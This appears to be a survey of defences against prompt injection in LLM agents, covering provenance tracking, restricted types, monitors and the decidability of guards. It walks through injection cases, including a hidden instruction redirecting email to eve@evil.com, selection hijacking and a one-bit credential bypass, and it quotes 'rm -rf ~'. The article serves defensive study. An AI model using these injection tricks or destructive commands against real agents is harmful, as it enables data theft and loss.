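On the other hand, a list of permitted syntax can exclude harmful programs that a type checker accepts. A loop that never ends is well typed in both Scala and Haskell, so LACUNA limits time and nesting. STELP blocked all 50 infinite loops in the test. Such a list is also easier to adopt, because most agent software is in Python and the list needs no new types.

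In a separate test, STELP gave the correct output for all 361 programs. The researchers had selected only programs that fitted the permitted syntax, so the result doesn't show how many useful programs that syntax would exclude.

### What the type checker costs

Developers have to write a typed function for every tool, and types such as `Owned` for every rule they want the compiler to enforce. The model then has to write code that type-checks against these definitions.

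Zhao and colleagues compared LACUNA with ordinary tool calls on 392 customer-service tasks from τ²-bench. DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% of the tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. That difference of 14 percentage points is substantial, although the paper describes the results as "on par". The difference was largest on the retail tasks, where the model solved 58.8% with LACUNA and 80.9% with ordinary calls. The weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite solved 29.1% of all tasks with LACUNA and 33.2% with ordinary calls.

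Rejected code accounts for some of the extra work. On the retail tasks, the compiler rejected 22.4% of the code DeepSeek's model wrote, and LACUNA requested new code 7.1 times per task on average. The compiler rejected 3.2% of the code Gemini's model wrote on retail tasks but 89% on telecom tasks, where the model made little progress. Zhao and colleagues suspect that models write worse Scala than Python because they have seen less of it in training.

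Programs needed much less repair when the model only had to search a collection of documents. On 830 difficult research questions, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the code from DeepSeek's model, and two-thirds of the questions needed no second attempt. The model answered 27.1% of them correctly. Zhao and colleagues conclude that type checking does not reduce accuracy here, but they did not run the same model with ordinary tool calls for comparison.

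ELBA needed even fewer repairs, averaging 0.13 per run, and only 7 of 2,688 runs exceeded the limit on attempts. Zhou and colleagues used stronger models, which probably helped.

The main drawback in testing came from the rules themselves, which reduced the number of tasks ELBA completed. Without any attack, ELBA completed 14 to 18 of 21 AgentDojo tasks involving the messaging service Slack with the rules off, depending on the model, and 8 to 10 with them on. CaMeL, an earlier system whose model has to write the whole program before reading any data, completed 4 to 6 with its own rules on. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL because its agents call the model again after reading data.

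None of AgentDojo's standard attacks succeeded, even without rules, so these attacks could not show whether the rules were useful. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a worst case. Whenever a subagent read a planted instruction, they replaced its task with that instruction. With the rules on, no attack succeeded in 735 runs per model. The table shows what happened without them, and how many tasks the agents completed in each case:

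| Model | Attacks that succeeded without rules | Tasks completed without rules | Tasks completed with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 310 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 275 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 114 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 195 | 494 | 294 |

The rules stopped every attack but also blocked about a third to nearly half of the tasks the agents would otherwise have completed. Zhou and colleagues suggest using such rules as a conservative filter in systems where a person approves actions. Actions that pass the rules can run without approval, and the person reviews only those the rules block.

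## Valid arguments that come from an untrusted source

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a web page and email the summary to `boss@company.com`. The page contains a hidden instruction to send it somewhere else. The agent could make either of these calls:

```json
{ "recipient": "boss@company.com", "body": "The page announces..." }
{ "recipient": "eve@evil.com", "body": "The page announces..." }
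```

Both recipients match any reasonable pattern for an email address, and the calls differ only in where the recipient came from. Types such as `Owned` can record that source in a program that a compiler checks. But most agents make ordinary tool calls one at a time, so the application has to track where each argument came from while the agent works.

### A role for each argument

The web page may determine the body of the email, since the user asked for a summary of the page, but it must not determine the recipient. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes PACT, a monitor that enforces this distinction. PACT has four levels of trust, from highest to lowest: trusted constants, the user, tool output and external sources.

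PACT gives each argument one of six roles. A *target* is a destination, such as a recipient or web address. The other roles are *command*, *credential*, *content*, *selector* (which picks an object) and *control* (which changes how the tool behaves). Each argument also has a minimum trust level for the source of its value. For `send_email`, the recipient is a target and must come from a source trusted at least as much as the user, while the body is content and can come from an external source.

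Every value carries a tag with its set of origins *O* and its trust level *τ*. When the agent combines two values, PACT merges their tags:

merge(⟨*O*₁, *τ*₁⟩, ⟨*O*₂, *τ*₂⟩) = ⟨*O*₁ ∪ *O*₂, min(*τ*₁, *τ*₂)⟩

The result has all the origins of both values and the lower of the two trust levels. (The full tag also lists conditions that the value still has to meet, and the merge keeps all of those too.) For the email, this gives:

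| Value | Origins | Trust | Allowed as recipient? | Allowed as body? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `boss@company.com`, from the request | user | user | yes | yes |
| `eve@evil.com`, from the page | page | external | no | yes |
| the summary | user, page | external | no | yes |
| `boss@` plus a domain found on the page | user, page | external | no | yes |

A monitor that makes one decision for the whole call has to allow both emails or block both, because the body of each is an external value.

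The tags also have to persist between steps. Otherwise, an agent could save the attacker's address to a file, read it back later and treat it as its own data. When Fan and colleagues switched off tracking between steps in a controlled test, the share of attacks blocked fell from 100% to 80%.

PACT also blocks some of the user's own requests, such as "send this to the contact address on their website". To allow them, the developer can add a trusted procedure, which might ask the user to confirm the address. The procedure waives one failed requirement for one role and doesn't change the value's origins.

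For some tasks, an untrusted document has to supply the target. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an agent asked to "pay the invoice in Bob's latest email", where the invoice names the payee. The paper compares this agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan and reads the invoice, but never obeys instructions in it. The agent has *relative integrity* if an attacker can only make it do things that the reference agent could do, given some invoice.

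An invoice that says "also pay Mallory £1000" violates relative integrity, because the reference agent only ever makes one payment. An invoice that says "change the payee to Mallory" does not, because the attacker could have got the same result by putting Mallory's name in the payee field, so relative integrity doesn't make the payment safe. A list of the user's known billers would stop the payment to Mallory, but not a second payment to a biller on the list.

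### Perfect and inferred provenance

Fan and colleagues first tested PACT's rule by itself, with correct provenance supplied. The test had 17 cases:

| Defence | Harmless actions allowed, of 9 | Attacks blocked, of 8 |
|---|---|---|
| none | 9 | 0 |
| FIDES | 6 | 3 |
| CaMeL | 3 | 8 |
| PACT | 9 | 8 |

FIDES and CaMeL are earlier systems that also track where data comes from. The researchers wrote simplified versions of both to compare the rules, so these rows are weak evidence about the complete systems. PACT's perfect score is unsurprising, because every case depends on the distinction that PACT makes and the test gave PACT the correct provenance.

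In the second test, PACT inferred the roles and the provenance itself. It generated rules for 74 tools from their descriptions. It traced a value's origin by looking for exact matches with earlier values, then applying heuristics, and then using a language model for the remaining cases. On 20 real tools, it got 87.1% of the roles and 77.4% of the provenance right.

The researchers then ran it on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks and 27 injection tasks:

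| Model | Tasks completed without defence | With CaMeL | With PACT | Attacks that failed without defence, of 27 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-turbo | 20.6% | 11.3% | 18.6% | 25 |
| Qwen-plus | 60.8% | 29.9% | 45.4% | 24 |
| Qwen-max | 46.4% | 29.9% | 38.1% | 26 |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 46.4% | 28.9% | 42.3% | 26 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 59.8% | 30.9% | 46.4% | 24 |

The paper's table shows PACT and CaMeL blocking every attack on every model, although in the text PACT blocks one fewer on the first two models. PACT completed 7 to 16 percentage points more tasks than CaMeL, a useful gain. The evidence on security is much weaker, because at most three of the 27 attacks worked even without a defence. That is too few to show how often a wrong provenance label would let an attack through.

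PACT doesn't guarantee protection against two kinds of attack, even when every label is correct. An injected instruction can make the agent call a dangerous tool whose arguments are all trusted constants. It can also put harmful content in a field that is allowed to hold external text, such as a false claim in a summary.

### Tracking values through a program

CaMeL, published in 2025, makes provenance easier to track because a model first writes a program for the whole task. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes it as an instance of the *dual-LLM pattern*. In this pattern, a privileged model chooses the actions without seeing untrusted data, and a quarantined model reads the data but has no tools. For the summary, the program could be:

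```python
page = fetch("https://evil.com")
summary = ask_quarantined_model("Summarise this page", page)
send_email("boss@company.com", summary)
```

The privileged model wrote the recipient into the program before the page was read, so the page cannot have influenced that choice. The code also shows that `summary` depends on `page`. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) explains that CaMeL labels data by provenance and enforces its policies when the program calls a tool. The paper criticises CaMeL's use of a restricted form of Python, because features such as exceptions make it hard to prove in advance where information can go, and proposes a purpose-built language with bounded loops and simple conditions.

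The main limitation is that the agent has to write the whole plan before it reads anything. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) points out that an agent fixing a bug cannot do this, because it has to inspect the code, run commands and revise its ideas.

PACE, a monitor that Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) describe in *PACE*, doesn't need a plan. It makes two checks immediately before each call:

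- The *effect check* lists what the call would do, such as sending an email to a certain address, and compares this with permissions derived only from the user's request.
- The *path check* keeps a graph of how data has moved during the task. If untrusted or secret data has a path to an unsafe call, PACE finds the cheapest way to cut every such path, for instance by blocking the call.

In the certified configuration, one of two that the paper describes, PACE always carries out the cut, and if the cut changes the call, PACE repeats the effect check on the new version. Li, Wang and colleagues prove that no chain from a protected source can then reach an unsafe effect through that call. They assume that the graph represents the chain, that all sources are labelled correctly and that each cut breaks the link. They give conditions under which the graph represents a chain, but these exclude text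 that the model has reworded, for example in a summary, without a provenance record.

All the experiments use the other configuration, which can restore a call that the path check blocked if the effect check accepts it. It can also repair a call without checking the result again. Restoring a blocked call undoes the cut, so the proof about paths no longer applies.

The likely reason is that the path check alone prevents the agent from completing most tasks. It reduced the share of tasks completed from 76.8% to 13.6% on part of AgentDojo, and from 66.7% to zero on AgentDyn, another benchmark. On AgentDyn, PACE proposed a cut for 5,842 of the 6,647 calls it examined (88%), and it never saved a call by rewriting an argument.

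On the full AgentDojo benchmark, the most successful group of attacks against the evaluated configuration worked between 0% and 8.1% of the time, depending on the model, compared with 48% to 100% without a defence. The agents completed at most three percentage points fewer tasks. But most of this security comes from the effect check, and the path theorem, the part of PACE that concerns provenance, doesn't cover these results.

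In these tests, the most effective group of attacks against CaMeL succeeded 28% of the time with a DeepSeek model and 36% with a GPT model, whereas Fan and colleagues found no successful attacks. The two papers used different models and attacks, so neither result is a reliable measure of CaMeL in general.

### Why labels spread

In ordinary code, `total = price + tax` depends only on `price` and `tax`, but when a language model writes a value, any part of its input may influence any part of its output. Applied strictly, the merge rule would therefore give every output the lowest trust level in the model's input. After the agent reads one web page, even a recipient that the user typed would count as external once the model copies it into a call. This spread of labels to data that the source did not affect is called *label creep*.

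Dongol analyses a defence called a "fence". As soon as the agent reads something untrusted, the fence withdraws every tool that an injection might make the agent call. He proves that this prevents injected payments, but it also stops the agent from paying a legitimate bill it has just read.

PACT's exact matching avoids some of the spread, because a recipient identical to the one in the user's request can keep the user's trust level. But exact matching can miss real influence. Suppose the user says, "If the report is positive, send it to Ana, otherwise to Ben." Either address would match the user's request, even though whoever wrote the report decides which one the agent uses.

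### Estimating what reached the output

*Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) estimates each input's influence on a model's output by comparing the two. Its system, PRISM, uses language models to assign each input one or more of 25 labels, such as "translation" or "fragment copy". Some labels mean that the input left no visible trace, and PRISM treats all the others as a flow from input to output. For example, a product review counts as reaching the output even if the model reduces it to a score of 4.

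In taint analysis, which follows untrusted data through a program, PRISM had an F1 score of 81.7%, compared with 47.5% for assuming that every input reaches the output and 62.8% for the best alternative. The paper calls PRISM sound relative to its labelling, so if the labellers wrongly decide that the model ignored an input, PRISM misses a real flow.

*Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) measures a model's *attention*, the mechanism that moves information between positions in the text. A small classifier uses these measurements to predict which inputs the model used to produce the output. The researchers prove that if no chain of attention leads from an input to the output, slightly changing that input does not affect the output.

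This would be enough for a proof if attention were ever exactly zero, but in practice every input receives at least a little. Very low attention doesn't rule out influence. In one of their counterexamples, an input with the value −1 receives about two billionths of the attention. If its value were 1, it would receive almost all the attention and change the output. The input's value therefore determines the result even when the input receives almost no attention, much as a false condition in an `if` statement determines that a block of code will not run.

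Sightline therefore offers a statistical guarantee. Suppose the researchers take one known flow from each of 999 groups of related programs. To miss at most 1% of flows, they set the threshold at the tenth-lowest score. If a flow from a new group is equally likely to rank anywhere among these scores, the chance that it scores below the threshold is at most 10 in 1,000.

In tests on programs it had not seen, Sightline missed about 1% of real flows and removed 44% to 66% of the false ones. When the researchers used it to track labels in an agent, it removed about half of the unnecessary labels, and no attack succeeded.

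These are good results for a tool for reducing false alarms, but they can't support a proof about a particular call. PACT's guarantee requires each tag to include every source that influenced the value, so it fails if a tag misses even one. The 1% rate is also an average over calls like those used to set the threshold, and an attacker can choose different kinds of inputs and keep trying. Even if the rate held for each of 100 independent attempts, the chance of at least one miss would be 63%.

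### Letting only a choice through

The application doesn't have to estimate the influence of untrusted text if it limits what that text can pass on. In *Better Privilege Separation for Agents by Restricting Data Types* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025), a quarantined agent reads the text but can return only whole numbers, decimals, Booleans and choices from a fixed list. A second agent, which has the tools, receives these values and never sees the text.

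A choice among *k* options carries at most log₂ *k* bits of information, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. For some typical answers, this gives:

| Answer | Possible values | Maximum information |
|---|---|---|
| Boolean | 2 | 1 bit |
| one of 16 file names | 16 | 4 bits |
| whole number from 1 to 1,000 | 1,000 | about 10 bits |
| 50 characters of free text, from 95 printable characters | 95⁵⁰ | about 328 bits |

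Ten Boolean answers from the quarantined agent carry at most 10 bits, so they have 1,024 possible combinations. An attacker who completely controls the agent can choose any of these combinations but cannot create another. If ordinary code acts on the answers, a developer can check what that code does in all 1,024 cases.

A whole number with no upper limit can encode any text, for example by writing each letter as a numeric code, although Jacob and colleagues argue that whole numbers cannot contain an instruction. A model might not decode the text, but the type doesn't prevent it from doing so. A developer who wants a firm limit on what a number can encode should give it a minimum and a maximum.

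For an online shopping agent, the quarantined agent reads each product review and returns one number for how much it supports the product and another for how relevant it is. The shopping agent receives the medians and the number of reviews. An attacker who writes one review can therefore have only a small effect, provided most of the others are genuine. This design stopped every attack in three test applications. The shopping agent and a calendar agent remained as useful as before, but a bug-fixing agent did not, presumably because the file name, line number and type of bug it receives leave out much of what a bug report explains.

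Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues (2026), in *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees*, apply the same idea to web pages. They replace untrusted parts of a page, such as comments and reviews, with placeholders. The agent can ask a quarantined model a question about any placeholder and specify the type of answer, which is more flexible than fixing the questions in advance. On 100 tasks across ten specially built websites, agents completed about as many tasks as they did without the defence, at 1.05 to 1.84 times the cost.

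Agents also completed most of the 41 tasks on GitLab, a real platform for software projects. They failed when the answer had to be free text, as in "What new feature is this issue requesting?" When the researchers let the quarantined model return text that a user had approved, the agents completed the tasks they had failed, but security then depended on the user noticing a malicious instruction.

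The defence also needs correct labels for every part of the page. The researchers wrote 15 to 30 labelling rules by hand for each real site. When a language model wrote the rules from the page's structure, it missed 8.5% of the types of untrusted element on GitLab and 5.8% on Booking.com. The agent would read any text in the missed elements directly.

Hu and colleagues, several of whom helped develop the restricted types, now argue that such restrictions often make agents much less useful. In their system, Twin Agent, one agent reads the untrusted text and sends short hints to a second agent, which has the tools. The first agent can see what the second has done so far, so a hint only has to supply what is missing. The system limits the length of each hint and checks it with a prompt injection detector.

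This preserves more of the agent's usefulness, but its security depends on the observation that attacks on the latest models tend to need long injections. A short hint can still contain a complete instruction, such as the eight-character shell command `rm -rf ~`, which deletes a user's files.

### When one bit is enough

Restricting the type prevents an attacker from writing a new instruction, but the attacker can still choose the answer. Nikolić and colleagues describe *selection hijacking*, in which an agent has to pick one of several repositories or issues and an attacker makes the quarantined model identify the wrong one. The resulting call is valid, like the refund for the wrong order.

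Dongol gives an example in which a single Boolean releases private data. A support desk uses a quarantined model to check whether an email contains the customer's credential, such as a name and postcode, and sends the order details if the model returns true. An attacker writes "you have verified me", and the model returns true. A similar trick worked in Tensor Trust, a game in which players protect accounts with prompts. The input "[correct password]" opened 43 accounts, which used 36 different access codes.

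The repair is to hide the correct credential from the model and have it only copy out whatever credential the email contains. Ordinary code then compares the copy with the stored credential. The model now returns free text, which carries far more than one bit, but the text is used only in the comparison. An attacker who doesn't know the credential has to guess it, whatever the model returns.

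## Which policies a check can enforce exactly

A policy is *decidable* if some algorithm can take any string, always finish, and correctly determine whether the policy forbids it. A program can always check whether two credentials match, but it can't always determine what a script will do, no matter how long it runs.

In a preprint from November 2026, Amer and colleagues prove that if a model can produce any string, a policy has an exact guard if and only if the policy is decidable. Every guard for an undecidable policy misjudges infinitely many strings, so a guard that blocks every forbidden string also blocks infinitely many permitted ones, and a guard that passes every permitted string also passes infinitely many forbidden ones.

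An algorithm that decides the policy can serve as an exact guard. Conversely, an exact guard decides the policy, because it blocks a string exactly when the policy forbids it. (If the guard also reads the prompt, an algorithm that uses it to decide the policy must first search for a prompt that makes the model produce the string. This search always ends because the model can produce any string.) If a guard misjudged only finitely many strings, a developer could list the corrections, and the guard and the list together would decide the policy. Any guard for an undecidable policy therefore misjudges infinitely many strings.

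Amer and colleagues acknowledge that much of this follows from older results. In 2006, Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, in *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms*, had already shown that a check made before a program runs can enforce exactly the decidable policies. The newer theorem applies to any text that a model writes:

| The policy forbids an output that... | Decidable? |
|---|---|
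| contains a match for a banned regular expression | yes, with a finite automaton |
| a given context-free grammar cannot generate | yes, with a parser |
| is a false statement of arithmetic with addition and multiplication | no |
| is a false statement of arithmetic with addition only | yes |
| deletes a file when run as a script | no |
| deletes a file within its first 1,000 steps when run as a script | yes, by simulating 1,000 steps |

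Order numbers, hostnames and the syntax of a query are all on the decidable side, although inclusion between context-free languages is not.

### Whether a script deletes a file

Suppose a model writes this Python script:

```python
n = 4
while is_sum_of_two_primes(n):
    n = n + 2
os.remove("/srv/reports/q3.txt")
```

The function tries every pair of smaller primes, so it always returns an answer. The loop tests 4, 6, 8 and so on, and the script deletes the report only if the loop reaches an even number that is not the sum of two primes. Goldbach's conjecture, which dates from 1742, is that no such number exists. To judge these four lines correctly, a guard would have to be right about whether the conjecture is true.

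The proof uses infinitely many scripts because a developer could build the right answer for any single script into the guard. For any program *p*, a developer can write a script that first simulates *p* without touching any files and then deletes the report. This script deletes the report exactly when *p* finishes, so an exact guard could determine whether any given program finishes.

Alan Turing proved in the 1930s that no algorithm can correctly predict what every program will do. If one existed, someone could write a program that applies the algorithm to its own text and then does the opposite of what the algorithm predicts.

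The same construction works for sending an email or opening a network connection. Rice's theorem (1953) was originally about the results programs return, and Amer and colleagues adapt it to the actions programs perform. A policy is undecidable if it depends only on what a program does and forbids some programs but not others.

Running a script in a sandbox can confirm that it deletes a file, but no similar procedure can identify every script that never deletes one. A script that has looped for a week may still delete the file a second later.

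A second language model cannot serve as an exact guard either, because it is also an algorithm. If it samples its answers at random, it misjudges some output with a probability of at least one half. Constrained decoding has a similar limit, since a decoder that produces only harmless scripts must leave out infinitely many harmless ones. One can still prove that a particular script is safe.

A developer might instead forbid any script that contains the text `rm`. A guard can enforce this different policy exactly, but it blocks `echo rm`, which only prints two letters, and passes `find . -delete`, which deletes files. Hamlen and colleagues describe a sound approximation for another undecidable policy, that a program must eventually finish. The check accepts only programs that finish within 100 steps, so it rejects a harmless program that needs 101.

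### How often a guard must be wrong

The theorem implies that a sound guard blocks infinitely many harmless scripts, but these may all be scripts that nobody would ever write. So the theorem doesn't imply a minimum error rate for a guard such as CARE.

Amer and colleagues show that the average error can be as small as anyone likes. Suppose a developer will tolerate blocking a permitted output 1% of the time. Some finite list of strings accounts for more than 99% of what the model writes. A guard that stores whether the policy permits each string on the list, and blocks everything else, is sound and blocks a permitted output less than 1% of the time. This proves that such a guard exists, but someone still has to find the correct answers to store. No single algorithm can find them for every list, because it could then decide the policy for any string by taking a list that contains only that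 string.

A low average error also gives little protection against an attacker, who can search for strings that the guard misjudges. Suppose a fraction *α* of all uses are attacks, each attack gets a forbidden output past the guard with probability *σ*, and each success causes a loss of at least *λ*. The expected loss per use is then at least *ασλ*, even if the guard almost never misjudges ordinary outputs. For example, if one use in a thousand is an attack, half of the attacks succeed and each success costs 10,000 dollars, the expected loss is at least 5 dollars per use.

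### A language without loops

An exact guard becomes possible if the model has to write in a more limited language. Suppose the language has only these commands:

- `copy` copies a file to another path if the file exists, and otherwise does nothing.
- `delete` removes a file if it exists.
- `if missing` runs one command if a file does not exist.

The language has no loops, and a script must give every path as fixed text. Here is a script that contains a `delete` command:

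```
copy q3.txt backup.txt
if missing backup.txt: delete q3.txt
```

The script ends after one pass through its lines, so the guard can simulate it. If no other program changes the files in the meantime, the outcome depends only on which of the two files exist at the start:

| `q3.txt` | `backup.txt` | Effect of `copy` | Effect of `delete` |
|---|---|---|---|
| exists | exists | replaces `backup.txt` | does not run |
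| exists | missing | creates `backup.txt` | does not run |
| missing | exists | none | does not run |
| missing | missing | none | runs but finds no file |

The script never deletes a file, and the guard passes it. A ban on the word `delete` would have blocked it.

The same method works for any language in which the guard can use a script's text to calculate an upper limit on how many steps the script will take. The language can include loops with a fixed maximum number of rounds, but not a command that runs an arbitrary Python program, because the original problem would return. Putting the Python program inside a JSON field would not help, since that changes the script's format but not what it can compute.

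Fixed paths keep the number of cases finite. If a script could read a path from a file, the guard would have to consider every path the file might contain. Even with fixed paths, the number of cases doubles with each file, so 30 files give more than a billion. An SMT solver can often avoid testing the cases one by one but may still be slow for some scripts.

Limiting the length of the model's output also makes every policy decidable, because there are only finitely many possible outputs and a guard could, in principle, store the correct answer for each. But there are more than 10¹⁹⁷ texts of just 100 printable characters, and the Goldbach script fits in a few hundred. For an undecidable policy, no algorithm can produce the right guard for every length limit. Amer and colleagues add that this doesn't prove that the exact guard for any particular limit needs a lot of computation.

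*Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified* (Franco and Gershenson, 2026) finds that safety is decidable for agents with limits on context, stored values and running time, but that the problem is PSPACE-complete even when the agent's description is known. All known algorithms for PSPACE-complete problems take exponential time in the worst case. *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (2026) also finds that exact evaluation is possible in finite models. The small language is more useful than a length limit because its scripts are simple enough to simulate.

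### Stopping the deletion when it happens

Controlling the Goldbach script while it runs is easy and doesn't require settling Goldbach's conjecture. A monitor can block the call if the script reaches `os.remove`, and if the loop never ends, the script never tries to delete anything.

Amer and colleagues' second theorem covers monitors that, before each action, check the sequence of actions so far, including the proposed one. The policy is a set of forbidden finite sequences, and no later action can make a forbidden sequence acceptable. An exact monitor exists if and only if an algorithm can decide whether a given finite sequence is forbidden.

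For the deletion policy, the algorithm only has to look for a deletion in the sequence. The monitor only has to recognise the next action, whereas the guard had to work out everything the script might do. Hamlen and colleagues give the example of a program that must never write to the boot sector, the part of a disk from which a computer starts. A monitor can enforce this rule exactly for all programs, which no check of the program's text can do.

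Hamlen and colleagues point out that a monitor can enforce any policy that an exact check of the text can, by running that check as soon as the program starts. Checking the text in advance can still be preferable, because a monitor may stop a script halfway through its task.

*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) establishes a similar limit for gates on agents' tool calls. One policy in the paper caps the total an agent can transfer to any recipient in a day. If the cap is 500 dollars and the agent has already sent 420, the gate allows a transfer of 80 dollars and blocks one of 81. Another forbids the agent to send anything after the user revokes access. Both policies depend only on the proposed call and recorded facts, so a gate can enforce them exactly.

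A third policy forbids emailing personal information to recipients who are not on an approved list. The gate can check recipients against the list exactly, but it needs a judge to decide whether the text contains personal information. Ray's theorem assumes the judge's answers are correct, so its guarantee does not cover the judge's mistakes.

### Rules that a monitor cannot enforce

Schneider showed in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) that a monitor that works by stopping a program can enforce only *safety properties*. These are rules that a program breaks at some definite point, such as "send no messages after reading a file". The rule that every customer who pays must eventually receive the service is not a safety property, because at any point the service could still arrive later. A monitor can prevent the seller from doing anything else after taking the payment, but it cannot make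 the seller provide the service.

Other rules compare what a program does with what it would have done in different circumstances. In an example from Hamlen and colleagues, a program must behave exactly as if a secret file did not exist. A monitor cannot enforce this rule, but the system can rewrite the program so that its folder listings leave out the file. A program that would have ignored the file behaves as before, and nobody has to work out which programs would have reacted to it. Pedro and colleagues similarly rewrite queries to hide other users' rows, without judging what each query was meant to do.

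A monitor also has to act at the right place. Suppose a script writes a second script, `clean.sh`, and sends it to another computer. A monitor that must prevent the delivery of harmful scripts has to decide whether `clean.sh` would delete anything, which is undecidable for arbitrary scripts. A monitor on the other computer would only have to block the deletion. This is a practical concern because one agent might write scripts and another might run them, and Franco and Gershenson showed that individually safe agents can be unsafe together.

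Some actions are beyond the monitor's control. *Runtime Enforcement With Partial Control* (2015) describes earlier work that distinguishes actions a monitor can prevent from actions it can only observe. An application can only observe a web search that runs on Anthropic's servers. Schneider gives the example of a rule that nobody may wait more than a certain number of seconds for a resource. A monitor cannot enforce this rule because stopping the program does not stop time from passing.

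Even when the monitor can stop an action, its definition of that action must cover every way of performing it. On Linux, `rm`, `find -delete` and Python's `os.remove` all delete files through a small group of requests to the operating system. A monitor that intercepts those requests catches all three, while a monitor that looks for the command `rm` misses the other two.

The monitor would still allow `copy q3.txt backup.txt`, which destroys the old contents of `backup.txt` without deleting a file. It enforces the rule against deletion exactly, but the rule doesn't protect the data. A ban on overwriting would protect the old backup, but it could also stop an agent from removing a password that someone saved in a public file. Amer and colleagues argue that blocking too much can be dangerous, so somebody is still responsible for choosing the rule, even when a check enforces it exactly.
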